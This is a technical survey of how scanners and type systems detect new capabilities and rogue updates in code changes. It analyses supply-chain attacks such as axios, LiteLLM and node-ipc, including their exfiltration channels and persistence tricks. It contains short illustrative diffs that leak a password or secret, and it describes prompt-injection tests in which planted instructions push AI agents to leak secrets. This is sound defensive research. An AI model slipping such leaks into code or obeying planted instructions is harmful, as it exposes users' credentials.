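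A related tool, depcaps, can check dependencies against a project's own list of permitted capabilities. For example, a team might allow one library only the RUNTIME capability. The result doesn't depend on what earlier versions of the code did.

### Paths that never run

A call graph records what could happen if every branch of the code ran. Google gives the example of a function that reads a file only if one of its parameters is `true`. A caller that always passes `false` is still assigned the FILES capability. For the same reason, a call graph doesn't show that a patch has deleted a consent check before an upload.

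Calls with several possible targets are a second source of false paths. In Go, a function can accept any value that has a `Write` method, such as a file, a network connection or a block of memory, and the value determines which code runs. The simplest way to build the graph is to draw an arrow from the call to the `Write` method of every type that has one. According to Go's *package cha*, this includes types that the program never creates. Another of Go's libraries estimates which types can reach each call and draws arrows only to their methods.

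Comparing the two versions' call graphs removes many false paths because they appear in both. But a patch can also create new false paths elsewhere in the code. For example, if it adds a type whose `Write` method sends data over the network, the simplest kind of call graph marks every function that calls `Write` on a value of unknown type as having network access. The reviewer then sees many functions reported as gaining network access, even though the patch may not have changed any of them.

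The table of sensitive functions can also be wrong. In *Measuring Least Privilege*, Adam Harvey of the Rust Foundation describes an experimental version of Capslock for Rust. The tool can't analyze the C library through which Rust programs reach the operating system, so it needs a list of what each Rust function does there. The developers generated the list automatically by running the test suites of Rust's compiler and standard library and recording the requests each function made to the system. The list can't yet separate functions that change the state of the system from functions that only check whether output is going to a terminal, because both use the same kind of request. Harvey expects that a finished tool would need people to review the list.

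### Calls that the graph misses

Calls missing from the graph are worse for security because nobody sees them. Rafieian, Hicks and Wei (2026), in *Agentic Root Cause Reasoning and Localization of Unsoundness in Static Call Graph*, ran Java programs and compared the calls that happened with the graphs that three established tools had built from the code alone. Across the three tools, they found 1,459 missing calls. This count doesn't show how often the tools miss calls in general, because some of the programs were tests written to be difficult and the researchers included only programs with at least one missing call.

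Analysis tools sometimes miss calls that a human reader could easily follow, even in code that isn't written to hide them. In one test program, a variable holds the text `"Target"`, the next line loads the class with that name, and the program then calls one of its functions. OPAL misses this call because it follows such calls only if the name appears directly in the loading instruction. In another case, WALA missed a call because the program had put an object into a standard Java map and taken it out again.

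The tools gave no warning in these cases, so a user would have assumed the graph was complete. To fix this, Rafieian and colleagues had an AI agent propose a cause for each missing call and insert a warning at the place in the tool's code where the problem arose. Their system kept a proposal only if a test program reproduced the problem, monitoring of the running program confirmed the cause, and the warning appeared when it should. On eight programs not used in this process, the modified tools warned of 75 to 83 percent of the causes. Such warnings would make a capability report easier to trust, though it would still miss about a fifth of the causes.

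*Call Graph Soundness in Android Static Analysis* (2024) reports that call graphs of real Android apps omit many functions that run in practice, partly because of implicit calls, which don't appear as ordinary calls in the app's code. It also summarizes earlier research on languages that run on Java's virtual machine. That research found that call graphs were complete for Scala and OCaml but not for Python or Ruby, where many calls are determined at runtime. The exporter is written in Python, so a Python counterpart of Capslock would probably miss more than Capslock does in Go.

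### Stating capabilities in function types

Instead of working out afterwards what each function can reach, a programming language can make programmers declare it. In one such design, a function can use the network only if it holds an object that grants network access. `notify` then needs that object, and `export_report` has to get it from its own caller. In the language Scala, the first line of the exporter would change like this:

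```diff
-def exportReport(report: Report): String
+def exportReport(report: Report, net: Network^): String
```

If the patch leaves this line unchanged, the exporter has no network access to pass to `notify`, and the program doesn't compile. If the patch changes the line, the new capability appears in the diff, and every function that calls the exporter must also supply network access. *PermRust* (2025) presents a proof of concept of this idea for Rust that allows only code that owns a token to perform input and output.

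Requiring the object is not enough, because a programmer could wrap `net` in a small function and pass that function on, giving its recipient network access without any mention of `net`. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) prevent this with capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3. A value's type lists the capabilities that the value can retain. A function of type `String ->{f} Unit` takes text and may use the file `f`, whereas a function of type `String -> Unit` may use no capability. If the exporter accepts a date formatter of type `Date -> String`, the compiler rejects any program that passes it a formatter that also uploads the date.

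Capture checking also makes it safe to have global capabilities, such as a console that any code can refer to. An object that uses one must declare it in a `uses` clause, so programmers don't have to pass it through every call. This loses some detail because Scala attaches a method's capabilities to the object that contains it. If the object already declares the network, another of its methods can start using it without a change to the declaration.

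Odersky and colleagues built this into TACIT, a system for AI agents. The agent writes its actions as short Scala programs, and TACIT compiles each one in a "safe mode" before running it. Safe mode forbids features that could prevent the compiler from tracking a capability, including runtime reflection, which also hides calls from call graphs. The program can reach outside resources only through a library that grants access to particular folders, commands or network hosts. Secret files arrive in a sealed wrapper, and the agent can only process their contents with functions that hold no capabilities or send them to a separate trusted model, whose answer is also sealed.

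The main safety experiment used a software project with a folder of secrets. Two models each went through 131 trials. Of these, 120 combined ordinary tasks with planted instructions to leak the secrets, and the other 11 were direct or deceptive requests for them. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Secure trials with sealed secrets | Secure trials with plain text |
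|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 131 of 131 | 129 of 131 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 131 of 131 | 120 of 131 |

The design predicts the perfect scores, because the benchmark tests exactly the kind of leak that the types prevent. Without that protection, the results depended on the model, as the right-hand column shows. MiniMax M2.5 leaked secrets in 8 of the 11 direct or deceptive requests. The models could still work with the secrets sealed, and Sonnet completed 99.2 percent of the ordinary tasks with the wrapper, compared with 83.3 percent without it. The researchers suspect the lower figure is partly an artifact, since Sonnet often ran out of turns or time.

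Odersky and colleagues also ran TACIT with two other models on AgentDojo, an existing test of planted instructions. One of the 1,926 attacks succeeded, when the agent quoted hotel reviews that mentioned the attacker's hotel. With the model o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 53 percent of the office tasks, compared with 81 percent for CaMeL, a defense that tracks data while a program runs. The researchers call the two systems' shares of completed tasks comparable, which is generous to TACIT for this model.

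Writing typed programs did little harm to the agents' performance on other tasks. In simulated customer service, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7 percent, down from 43.3 percent, or five fewer issues. In the customer service tests, at most 7.9 percent of the programs needed another attempt after a compiler error, and one or two attempts were usually enough.

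None of these experiments tested the detection of new capabilities in a code change. On SWE-bench Lite, the compiler checked the Scala programs the agent used to read files and run commands, but not the patches the agent wrote. An agent with permission to edit the exporter could have added the call to `notify` as text in a Python file, and the compiler would not have checked it. The protection described above would require the exporter itself to be written in Scala with capture checking switched on.

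Adoption for agents takes fairly little work. The shared library has about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each new field of use, such as airline bookings, needs a few hundred more. Somebody also has to vouch by hand for library code that uses forbidden features internally. The compiler can't check programs that the agent starts, the same weakness that Deno warns about, so Odersky and colleagues also recommend a short list of permitted commands and a sandbox (a restricted environment for running code).

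An existing application takes much more work. The researchers consider Scala 3 the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in its types. Adding the feature to another mainstream language would mean extending its type system and restricting what programs can do. They expect this to take longer than it did starting from Scala.

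## Can a scanner tell where the data goes?

Suppose the exporter loads its data from a database, using a password from the environment, and then posts the report to the company's chat service. A patch changes one line:

```diff
 database.password = os.environ["DB_PASSWORD"]
 rows = database.load()
-notify("Report exported", render(rows))
+notify("Report exported", render(rows) + database.password)
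```

Everyone in the chat can now read the database password. The only new thing is the password's route through the program, which already read that variable, contacted chat.example and called `notify`. C(after) − C(before) is therefore empty at every level of detail described so far.

Attackers can send data to a new destination without adding a new capability. The npm package postmark-mcp let AI assistants send email through Postmark, an email delivery service that had nothing to do with the package. According to the security company Koi, which found the attack, version 1.0.16 added a single line that sent a blind copy of every email to the package developer's own server. A public malware record, OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), also lists 1.0.16 as the first malicious version. Postmark says the attacker had built up trust over 15 earlier versions. The package already needed network access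 to send email, so the malicious line didn't have to add any.

### Comparing routes instead of calls

Data-flow analysis follows values through a program. Security tools most often use a form called taint analysis. It takes a list of sources, such as functions that read private data, and a list of sinks, such as functions that send data out, and searches for paths from a source to a sink. Some of the CodeQL queries for npm updates did this for fixed patterns, such as an encoded string that ends up in a shell command.

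da Costa, Medeiros and colleagues (2021), in *Exploring the Use of Static and Dynamic Analysis to Improve the Performance*, compared such paths between two versions of Android apps. They had 96 pairs, each with a harmless and a malicious version of the same app. A tool called FlowDroid listed the source-to-sink paths in each version, and any path found only in the malicious version counted as a detection. This caught 58 of the 96.

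The experiment included no harmless updates, so it did not measure a false positive rate. Harmless updates also add new paths, and a useful comparison has to ignore most of them.

### How RogueOne compares two versions

Sofaer, David and colleagues (2024), in *RogueOne*, tackle this problem for npm packages. They look for rogue updates, in which an attacker has hidden malicious code in a new version of a harmless package. RogueOne works as follows:

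1. It runs both versions through abstract interpretation, a simulation that uses placeholder values instead of real input. This lets it explore both sides of a branch. To save time, it can skip large files that the update didn't change.
2. It reduces what happens in the simulation to four operations: importing a package, reading a property of an object, setting a property, and calling an outside function.
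3. From these it builds a graph of the program's objects, with two types of arrow. A data-flow arrow from A to B means that B's value depends on A's. An ownership arrow means that the code that created A can also control B.
4. It groups the objects into trust domains by origin. Everything that ownership arrows reach from an imported package belongs to that package's domain.
5. It lists the flows between domains. There is a flow from domain A to domain B if data-flow arrows from A reach an object that belongs to B.
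6. It subtracts the old list from the new one and flags the update if anything remains.

RogueOne treats built-in objects such as `process`, which holds the environment variables, as if they were imported. It gives the unknown program that will use the package a domain called `:caller`. By default, it puts all the fixed strings and numbers in the package's own code in one domain, `:local`.

One of the paper's examples resembles the chat patch. Here it is in shortened form:

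```diff
 secret = process.env.SECRET_KEY
 vault = require('secure-store')
 vault.key = secret
 board = require('public-store')
 board.publish(vault.query('...').publicData)
+board.publish(secret)
```

The old version reads a secret, uses it to open a private store, and publishes some of the private store's data in a public one. The new line publishes the secret itself. It calls a function that the line above already called, but the list of flows grows:

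```text
Before:  process → secure-store
         secure-store → process
         secure-store → public-store

After:   the same three, and
         process → public-store
```

The first two flows exist because `secret` belongs to two domains. It comes from `process`, and the assignment to `vault.key` also makes it part of `secure-store`. The new flow is in the result of `board.publish(secret)`. That result belongs to `public-store`, whose function produced it, and its value depends on the secret from `process`. RogueOne flags the update.

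In the other example, a program downloads data with the library axios and saves it with `fs`, Node's file module. The update adds a second call that saves data from failed requests under a new file name, `error.log`. A comparison of paths between individual calls would report this change, but RogueOne doesn't because data already flowed from axios to `fs`.

The grouping is based on the idea that one developer controls everything a package produces. If a program already passes data from `axios` to `fs`, passing more of it requires no additional trust. RogueOne treats nearly everything outside the package as potentially sensitive, so it doesn't need a list of suspicious functions.

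The comparison can catch an attack that arrives through a new dependency. In the attack on event-stream, a package for processing data streams, a new maintainer added a dependency called flatmap-stream that contained malicious code. event-stream never called any of the dependency's functions, but it passed the imported object on to its users, which created a flow from flatmap-stream to `:caller`.

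RogueOne also analyzes dependencies where it can, to avoid flagging every new one. If data sent to a dependency can't reach anywhere it couldn't already reach, RogueOne removes the flows to and from that dependency.

### Results against Maloss and Amalfi

Sofaer and colleagues tested RogueOne on two datasets. The single-update set has 341 updates, each from a different package. Of these, 41 are known rogue updates and 300 are updates they presumed harmless. Half of the 300 came from the most depended-upon packages and half from random ones. The multi-version set has 333 updates from only 12 packages, and 7 of the updates are rogue.

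Maloss, one of the two systems they compared it with, looks for suspicious functions and the flows between them, and also installs the package in a monitored environment. In one mode, it compares two versions and flags only new suspicious functions. For the other system, Amalfi, Sejfia and Schäfer (2022), in *Practical Automated Detection of Malicious npm Packages*, trained classifiers on how a package's use of capabilities changes between versions, the time between the versions and the type of version number change. In their example, the malicious version of jasmin, a web framework, handled password fields, read cookies and encoded data for sending. Each of these is common in web code, but the previous version had done none of them.

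| System | Rogue, single-update set (41) | False positives (300) | Rogue, multi-version set (7) | False positives (326) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| RogueOne, default | 31 | 14 (4.7%) | 7 | 17 (5.2%) |
| RogueOne, paranoid | 38 | 120 (40.0%) | 7 | 83 (25.5%) |
| Maloss | 14 | 110 (36.7%) | 7 | 272 (83.4%) |
| Maloss, new functions only | 5 | 8 (2.7%) | 1 | 2 (0.6%) |
| Amalfi, best classifier | Not tested | Not tested | 2 | 12 (3.7%) |

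The comparison with Amalfi is weak evidence because it rests on only seven attacks. Amalfi's developers couldn't share the code or the trained models, so only their published results on the multi-version set were available. Maloss is designed mainly for packages that are malicious from their first release, which puts it at a disadvantage here.

On the single-update set, RogueOne's default setting caught six times as many attacks as the comparison of suspicious functions, with six more false positives. Much of this lead may come from RogueOne's broad coverage rather than its tracing of data. In 22 of the 41 rogue updates, the attacker added code that steals passwords, card numbers or other data from web pages. RogueOne caught all 22, typically through a new flow from `:local` to `document`, the object that represents the page in a browser. That flow appears when a package starts passing fixed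 text to the web page. A comparison of functions could probably have caught many of these updates too if its list had included the browser's functions.

### Attacks that use existing flows

The default setting missed all ten attacks that Sofaer and colleagues call camouflaged. These also steal data in the browser, but the attacker put the code into a package that already used the same functions. The package or one of its dependencies already passed fixed text to `document`, so the malicious code added no flow between domains. (The paper's breakdown by attack type implies an eleventh miss, a file attack that the simulation couldn't process, but its main results count ten misses.)

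Of the cases in the test, these ten are the closest to the problem of capabilities already present in the code, and the default setting is too coarse for them. The paranoid setting gives every fixed string and number its own trust domain, so a new web address in the attacker's code creates a new flow even if the function that receives it was already there. This setting caught eight of the ten. In the other two, the simulation failed on loops unrelated to the attack.

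The drawback is that the paranoid setting flags almost any edit that changes some text. Across both datasets, 127 of its 203 false positives came from new data of this kind, such as a reworded log message, a renamed file or an adjusted search pattern.

RogueOne would probably miss the postmark-mcp backdoor in the same way. If earlier versions already passed some fixed text to the email library, the attacker's address adds no new flow by default, though the paranoid setting would treat the address as new. The chat patch is easier to catch because the password comes from the environment, not from a string in the code. But if the exporter already sent any environment variable, such as a token for logging in to the chat service, through the same networking library, RogueOne would report no new flow, because it compares packages rather than individual secrets and servers.

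Data-flow analysis can also miss an attack that involves no sensitive flow. One malicious Android app in the study by da Costa and colleagues differed from the original only in the advertising ID in its settings file. The changed ID sent the advertising income to someone else. None of the tools that looked for new sensitive calls detected it.

### False alarms, failures and running time

Most of RogueOne's false positives in its default setting come from gaps in its analysis. The largest group, 2.1 percent of all harmless updates, involved new dependencies that RogueOne couldn't analyze and so treated as if they had access to the system. Install scripts in languages other than JavaScript caused another 0.8 percent, because RogueOne flags them without analyzing them. Unfamiliar built-in functions and unsupported JavaScript features together caused about 1.1 percent.

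The remaining 0.8 percent are updates that started using a system function, for example to access files or the network. Sofaer and colleagues count these as errors because the updates were harmless, although they did add capabilities.

A reviewer usually needed no more than two minutes to check a false positive, with the new flows and the diff on screen. That is manageable for a team checking its own dependencies, but not for a whole registry. npm receives about 674,300 updates a month, according to figures that Wyss, Tassio and colleagues cite in *Evaluating LLM-Based Detection of Malicious Package Updates in npm*. A false positive rate of 4.7 percent would produce nearly 32,000 false alarms a month, which would take more than 1,000 hours to review at two minutes each.

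RogueOne's running time varies widely. Nine out of ten packages took less than four seconds, but the average was 226.7 seconds, and five updates reached the one-hour limit. Without the option to skip unchanged files, 140 would have reached it. Sofaer and colleagues treated every timeout or error as a harmless verdict because they expected most companies to do the same. An attacker could exploit this by adding code that makes the analysis fail. The researchers saw no rogue update whose malicious code caused a timeout, but an attacker who knew about RogueOne would have more reason to try.

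Wyss and colleagues later ran the default setting on more packages to compare it with language models. Of 2,000 ordinary updates, it flagged 124 and failed to produce a verdict for 160, or 8 percent. Among the updates it finished, the false positive rate was 6.7 percent.

RogueOne also caught 39 of 46 malicious updates, missed 5 and failed on 2. That is better than the original 31 of 41, which is odd because the 46 include all the malicious updates from the original test, minus duplicates, and only five new ones. Wyss and colleagues found that RogueOne was most likely to miss heavily obfuscated code and branching loops, whereas Sofaer and colleagues attributed nearly all their misses to camouflage. The default setting's performance on camouflaged attacks is therefore less certain than the original result of zero out of ten suggests.

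### Tracing data or listing new functions?

Listing new functions takes little computation and works even when the scanner can't follow the values, which is often the case in JavaScript. Nguyen, Ho and colleagues (2025), in *Leveraging Code Slicing for LLMs-based Malicious NPM Package Detection*, searched for paths from sources to sinks in npm packages that call at least one sensitive function. They found a path in only 56 percent of the malicious packages and 33 percent of the harmless ones. Code generated while the program runs, obfuscation and callbacks (functions that run after another task finishes) can all stop a scanner from following a value. The researchers also limited the analysis of each package to three minutes.

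When tracing works, it removes a lot of irrelevant code. The paths that Nguyen and colleagues extracted kept 73.7 percent of the lines with sensitive functions in malicious packages but only 9.4 percent in harmless ones. A simpler method that followed only the order in which statements can run, without data flow, achieved part of this benefit, keeping 73.4 percent of these lines in malicious packages and 15.9 percent in harmless ones.

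The route can also run partly outside the code. In *From Instructions to Exploits*, Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026) studied skills, which are packages of written instructions and scripts for AI agents. The instructions in one skill for editing presentations had the agent run a backup script on the finished file, and the script uploaded the file to a stranger's server. The instructions looked routine, and the script only uploaded whatever file it received. Their scanner translates the instructions into simple program statements so it can trace values through both the instructions and the scripts. On 117 malicious and 117 harmless skills, it reached an average recall of 95.2 percent and a precision of 80.2 percent. It examines one version at a time, so it can't detect whether an update introduced the route.

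The Android study compares the two approaches most directly. FlowDroid's new paths and a simpler static check for new sensitive calls caught the same 33 of the 96 malicious apps. The paths caught another 25, and the calls another 9. Running both would have caught 67, so tracing works better as an addition to a list of new functions than as a replacement for it.

For code review, it would make sense to trace only the most important values, such as passwords and tokens, which should also be faster. The simulation engine behind RogueOne has an option to ignore paths that can't reach a few chosen functions, but RogueOne leaves it off because it has to follow nearly all paths. A scanner that checks only whether a secret can now reach the network could use this option.

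## What can install scripts do, and what did recent attacks add?

Unlike the new code in the examples so far, an install script can run before anybody runs the program. *Killing Two Birds with One Stone* (2023), a study of malicious npm and PyPI packages, distinguishes three times when a package's code can start: during installation, when a program imports the package, and when the program calls one of its functions.

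### How installing or building a package runs code

A JavaScript package has a manifest, `package.json`, which lists its dependencies and scripts. During installation, npm runs the commands in the manifest's `preinstall`, `install` and `postinstall` entries. As Guo and colleagues note, these commands have all the privileges of the user who installs the package, so they can read that user's files and keys. If a package contains a file called `binding.gyp`, npm also starts a build to compile its code, even if the manifest lists no install script.

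Python packages come in two formats. A wheel is already built, so pip, Python's standard installer, normally just copies its files into place. A source distribution still needs building, so pip runs the package's own build code, traditionally a file called `setup.py`.

Rust dependencies can run code at build time. Cargo, Rust's package manager, compiles and runs a dependency's `build.rs` file, and the compiler executes procedural macros, which are functions that generate code. According to *Install script allowlists* (2026), a survey of package managers, both happen without a sandbox during everyday commands such as `cargo build` and `cargo test`. Go, by contrast, compiles downloaded packages without running them.

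Suppose the report exporter is a JavaScript program, and the patch for its date format adds a library:

```diff
 "dependencies": {
+  "example-dates": "1.0.0",
   "example-render": "2.3.1"
 }
```

This change contains no program code, but it can do more than a thousand new lines in a function that nobody calls. If `example-dates` has an install script and the package manager allows it, the script runs on every laptop and build machine that installs the exporter's dependencies, even if the exporter never imports the library.

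*Make install scripts opt-in*, a 2026 proposal to change npm's default, adds two reasons why reviewers may be too late to stop an install script. Many organizations run `npm install` automatically on each pull request, so the script can run before anyone has read the change. The new dependency may also appear only in the lock file, which records the exact version of every package. GitHub hides large lock file diffs by default.

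### How common install scripts are

Zahan, Zimmermann and colleagues examined the manifests of 1.49 million npm packages in *What are Weak Links in the npm Supply Chain?* (2021) and found install scripts in 2.2 percent of them. Install scripts appeared in 2.4 percent of 14,892 popular packages and in 93.9 percent of 3,635 known malicious packages.

Even with those figures, a rule that flags every install script would mostly flag harmless packages, because malicious ones are rare. In a hypothetical registry of a million packages, 1,000 of them malicious, the rule would flag about 939 malicious packages and about 22,000 harmless ones, a precision of about 4 percent. Reading the scripts helps only somewhat. Zahan and colleagues searched install scripts in the real registry for words that had appeared in malicious ones, such as the names of download programs and password files. They found 74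 packages, of which 11 were malicious.

The registry data dates from June 2021, and the share may well be lower now. *Make install scripts opt-in* describes a shift toward publishing precompiled code for each operating system, which removes the most common legitimate reason for an install script. Some popular packages still depend on install scripts. Socket, a security company, lists the image library sharp, which may need compiling, and the testing tools Cypress and Playwright, which download large programs during installation.

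Malicious Python packages also tend to run their harmful code early. *Unveiling Malicious Logic* (2025) labels 291 places in such packages that determine when the harmful code starts. Of these, 266 involve installation or build steps, and 25 involve importing the package.

### What package managers block by default

npm ran dependencies' install scripts automatically until July 2026, when GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026) announced version 12. The table gives the current defaults, with the rows for tools other than npm based on *Install script allowlists*, which dates from June 2026.

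| Tool | Code that can run | Default |
|---|---|---|
| npm 12 (JavaScript) | Install scripts and automatic native builds | Blocked until the project approves them |
| pnpm 10 and later, Deno (JavaScript) | Install scripts | Blocked until the project approves them |
| Bun (JavaScript) | Install scripts | Blocked, except for a built-in list of well-known packages |
| pip (Python) | Build code in source distributions | Runs, but a setting can refuse all source distributions |
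| Cargo (Rust) | `build.rs` and procedural macros | Runs, and users can't switch it off for a dependency |
| Go | None | Nothing to block |

(*Install script allowlists* and *Make install scripts opt-in* disagree about whether newer versions of Yarn, another JavaScript package manager, block scripts by default.)

When npm 12 blocks a script, it prints a warning and the installation still succeeds. According to Socket, a package that needed compiling then fails when the program tries to load it. Projects can prevent this by approving the scripts they need. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) recommends committing the list of approved scripts, which npm keeps in `package.json`.

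The committed list works as a baseline, much like capcheck's lock file of capabilities. By default, an approval covers one exact version, so a new release with an install script needs a new approval, which appears in the diff. A project can also approve a package by name, which covers all its future versions.

An early draft of the proposal contained a more direct check for new capabilities. npm would have compared each package with the lock file and blocked its install script if the package had not had one before. The idea was dropped, partly because exact-version approvals already cover that case and partly because the check would miss a package that replaced a harmless install script with a malicious one.

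### tj-actions: a change to a build step

An attack in March 2025 reached its victims through their build workflows, the automated steps that test, build or publish a project. Many workflows include ready-made steps called GitHub Actions. One of them, tj-actions/changed-files, lists the files a pull request changed.

Projects usually refer to an action by a version tag, and whoever controls the action can move the tag. According to OSV's *CVE-2025-30066* (2025), the attacker pointed the tags from v1 to v45.0.7 to a single malicious commit. The UAE Cyber Security Council reports that the action then printed secrets in the build logs. *Supply Chain Compromise of Third-Party GitHub Action, CVE-2025-30066* (2025), an alert from the US cybersecurity agency CISA, lists access keys, GitHub and npm tokens, and private encryption keys among those secrets. The advisory text in Fluid Attacks' *CVE-2025-30066*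 reports more than 23,000 affected repositories.

The tags pointed to the malicious commit on 14 and 15 March, and CISA published its alert on 18 March. The attack used no install script, and projects that used the action had no diff to review because their workflow files still named the same version. A scanner could have caught the change only by downloading the code behind the tag and comparing it with an earlier copy. The addition would then have been obvious, since a step that lists changed files has no reason to collect npm tokens. Moving the tags did not affect workflows that named an exact commit.

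### Nx and axios: install scripts

On 26 August 2025, attackers published malicious versions of several packages belonging to Nx, a build tool with about six million installs a week. *S1ngularity*, the maintainers' post-mortem by Strumpflohner, reports that a post-install script searched the user's machine for sensitive data and tried to use AI tools it found there, such as Claude and Gemini. The script then used GitHub's command-line program to upload the results to a public GitHub repository. The maintainers advise users to check their terminal's startup file for a shutdown command, so the script apparently wrote to files too.

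The script read files and credentials, wrote files and started other programs. A scanner that looks for network functions could easily have missed the upload, because another program sent the data. Rules for process execution or changed install scripts would have had more to flag.

A check for newly added install scripts might have missed the malicious script in the main `nx` package. The sample approval list in *Make install scripts opt-in* includes two later, ordinary releases of `nx`, which suggests that harmless versions have install scripts too. If so, a project that had approved `nx` by name would also have approved the malicious script, but approving only an exact version would have blocked it.

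Community members alerted the maintainers, who then saw that the packages lacked provenance, a signed record of where a package comes from, and concluded that someone had bypassed their release process. Strumpflohner puts the exposure at four hours, while Kurmi (2025) puts it at just over five in *s1ngularity*, an account from the security company StepSecurity.

The attackers had obtained the publishing token through a flaw in one of the project's build workflows. They put a malicious build script on a temporary branch, had the publishing workflow run it, and deleted the branch. Lamb and colleagues describe an Nx commit that sends a publishing token to an outside address, and this commit appears to be that step. A scanner that examined only pull requests to the main branch would have missed it.

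The March 2026 attack on axios, a library for web requests with about 101 million downloads a week, needed only a new dependency. According to the lead maintainer's post-mortem, quoted by Solar Designer (2026), in *Axios Supply-Chain Attack [v1.14.1] [0.30.4]*, the attacker posed as a company founder, invited the maintainer to a convincing Slack workspace and then to a video meeting, and got him to install malware that looked like a missing component. The attacker then used the maintainer's npm credentials to publish two versions of axios that depended on a package called `plain-crypto-js`.

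The dependency's name imitates the real package `crypto-js`. *Compromised axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT* (Tafani-Dereeper, 2026) describes how the dependency downloaded and ran a remote access tool, which lets an attacker control the machine. An install script started the download, so axios never had to call the dependency.

The times below are from the post-mortem, in UTC:

| Time | Event |
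|---|---|
| 30 March, 05:57 | The attacker publishes the first version of `plain-crypto-js` |
| 31 March, 00:21 | The attacker publishes axios 1.14.1 |
| About 01:00 | The attacker publishes axios 0.30.4, and outsiders detect the attack |
| 01:38 | Another axios developer opens a pull request to mark the versions as unsafe and contacts npm |
| 03:15 | npm removes both versions |

Users also reported the problem on the project's GitHub page, but the attacker deleted their reports with the maintainer's account.

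Comparing the kinds of access in axios's own code before and after the change would have found nothing new, since axios has always used the network. A rule that flags new dependencies would have caught the addition of `plain-crypto-js`, which was less than a day old. Scanning that package would have revealed its install script. The axios releases also had no counterpart on GitHub, which Willison (2026), in *Supply Chain Attack on Axios Pulls Malicious Dependency from npm*, considers a useful warning sign.

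According to the United Nations University's *When trust becomes a weapon*, the dependency's manifest showed no trace of the install script after an infection, so the scan had to happen before installation or on a fresh copy. npm 12 would have blocked the script by default, but it came out more than three months later.

### LiteLLM and node-ipc: no install script

LiteLLM is a Python package that programs use to send requests to language models. On 24 March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of it. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) describes code that searched for environment variables, SSH keys (used to log in to other machines), cloud credentials and database passwords. The code encrypted what it found and sent it to models.litellm.cloud, an official-looking address that did not belong to the company.

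In litellm 1.82.7, the malicious code was in `proxy_server.py`, so it ran only if something imported that file. Version 1.82.8 also added `litellm_init.pth`. Python processes `.pth` files, which can contain code, every time it starts. Willison (2026) points out in *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8* that installing the package was therefore enough to trigger the malicious code, without importing it. Blocking install scripts would not have helped, because the file only has to be in the right folder the next time Python starts.

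LiteLLM needs network access and API keys for its normal work, so the coarsest comparison of the two versions would probably have found little or nothing new. A finer comparison would have found a new network destination, access to SSH keys and, in 1.82.8, a file that runs automatically. A rule that flags new `.pth` files would have been the simplest check and needed no code analysis, but it would have missed 1.82.7.

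The first report to PyPI came from FutureSearch (2026), an AI company. According to Integrity360's *When security scanners become the weapon*, FutureSearch's researchers noticed the attack at 11:48 UTC because the `.pth` file started so many copies of itself that their machine crashed. That time is hard to reconcile with LiteLLM's statement that the packages were available from 10:39 for about 40 minutes before PyPI quarantined them. LiteLLM also advises anyone who installed the package before 16:00 to check for an infection, and its *Security townhall updates* (2026) gives 16:00 as the time by which the versions had been deleted. The packages were probably available for longer than 40 minutes. Either way, discovery depended partly on the attackers' mistake, and a version that didn't crash the machine might have gone unnoticed for longer.

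node-ipc, a JavaScript library that lets programs exchange messages, is the clearest case of an attack inside ordinary program code. OSV's *MAL-2026-3744* (2026) records three malicious versions, which someone published on 14 May 2026 from a maintainer's account. Each had the same 80 kilobytes of obfuscated code at the end of an existing file. The code collected more than 100 categories of sensitive files and smuggled them out in DNS queries, the lookups that computers use to turn a name such as example.com into a numerical address.

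Datadog Security Labs' *Backdoored node-ipc npm releases steal developer credentials through DNS queries* (2026) confirms that the malicious code ran when a program loaded the package, not through an install script. Semgrep's *Not Your IPC, but node-ipc* (2026) reports that the malicious versions were available for about two hours.

Comparing the code with the previous version could have flagged the obfuscation itself as new. A list of network functions that covered only web requests would have missed the DNS queries even if the code had been readable.

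Blocking install scripts gives attackers a reason to put their code elsewhere, so more of them may now write code that runs on import. About a week after npm 12 appeared, Microsoft's *Unpacking AsyncAPI npm supply chain compromise import time payload delivery* (2026) described five malicious package versions that worked this way, but one attack so soon after the change doesn't establish a trend.

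### Secrets that leave the machine

All five attacks involved stolen credentials. Willison also reports credential theft in the axios case. The pattern predates these attacks. Zahan and colleagues could read the commands of 485 malicious npm packages directly in the manifest, and 344 of those packages sent data such as the machine's name, password files or SSH keys to an outside server.

A scanner can look for this combination by requiring two findings, a new secret read and a new way for data to leave. But in these attacks the second half took many forms:

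| Attack | How the secrets left | Would a rule for web requests see it? |
|---|---|---|
| tj-actions | Text in the build log | No |
| Nx | GitHub's command-line program | Probably not |
| axios | Malware downloaded during installation | Only the download, if it scans the dependency |
| LiteLLM | Web request to a look-alike address | Yes |
| node-ipc | DNS queries | No |

A useful rule therefore has to treat process execution, DNS lookups and log output as possible ways for data to leave. This causes more false alarms, particularly for logs, since almost every program writes them.

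Even a perfect check of every pull request would have missed the LiteLLM and node-ipc attacks, because the attackers uploaded their versions straight to the registry. LiteLLM's maintainers found no malicious code in their main branch, and Wiz's *node-ipc npm distribution compromised* reports the same about node-ipc's repository. Comparing the published package with its source code would have exposed the extra code in both cases. LiteLLM later did this to verify its older releases.

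Companies that used the four packages would have seen at most a new version number in their own diffs. Waiting before updating is a simple defense for them. GitHub says that since July 2026 its update tool, Dependabot, has waited until a release is at least three days old before proposing it, except for security fixes. The malicious versions of all four packages were gone long before they were three days old, but only because somebody else had installed or scanned them first.

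## What does running the changed code reveal?

The recent attacks sent secrets out of the machine in many different ways, but these differences matter less once the code is running. A program has to make a system call to the operating system's kernel to open a connection, write a file or start another program, even if its source code is obfuscated. Behavioral analysis runs the code in a sandbox and records these calls.

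### Recording two versions

Ohm (2021), in *Software Supply Chain Angriffe*, used this method to compare versions of npm packages:

1. He installed the old version in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that starts every test in the same clean state.
2. The Linux program strace logged each system call.
3. He translated the relevant calls into behaviors. For example, `execve` means a new process, `connect` a network connection, and `open` with a write option a changed file.
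4. He did the same for the new version and subtracted the old list from the new one.

For the original exporter patch, the subtraction would leave a connection to collector.example if the upload ran. The recording would not show that the program read `REPORTS_TOKEN`, because Linux passes environment variables to a program when it starts, and reading one later takes no system call. The recording also wouldn't show the token being sent, because HTTPS encrypts the request.

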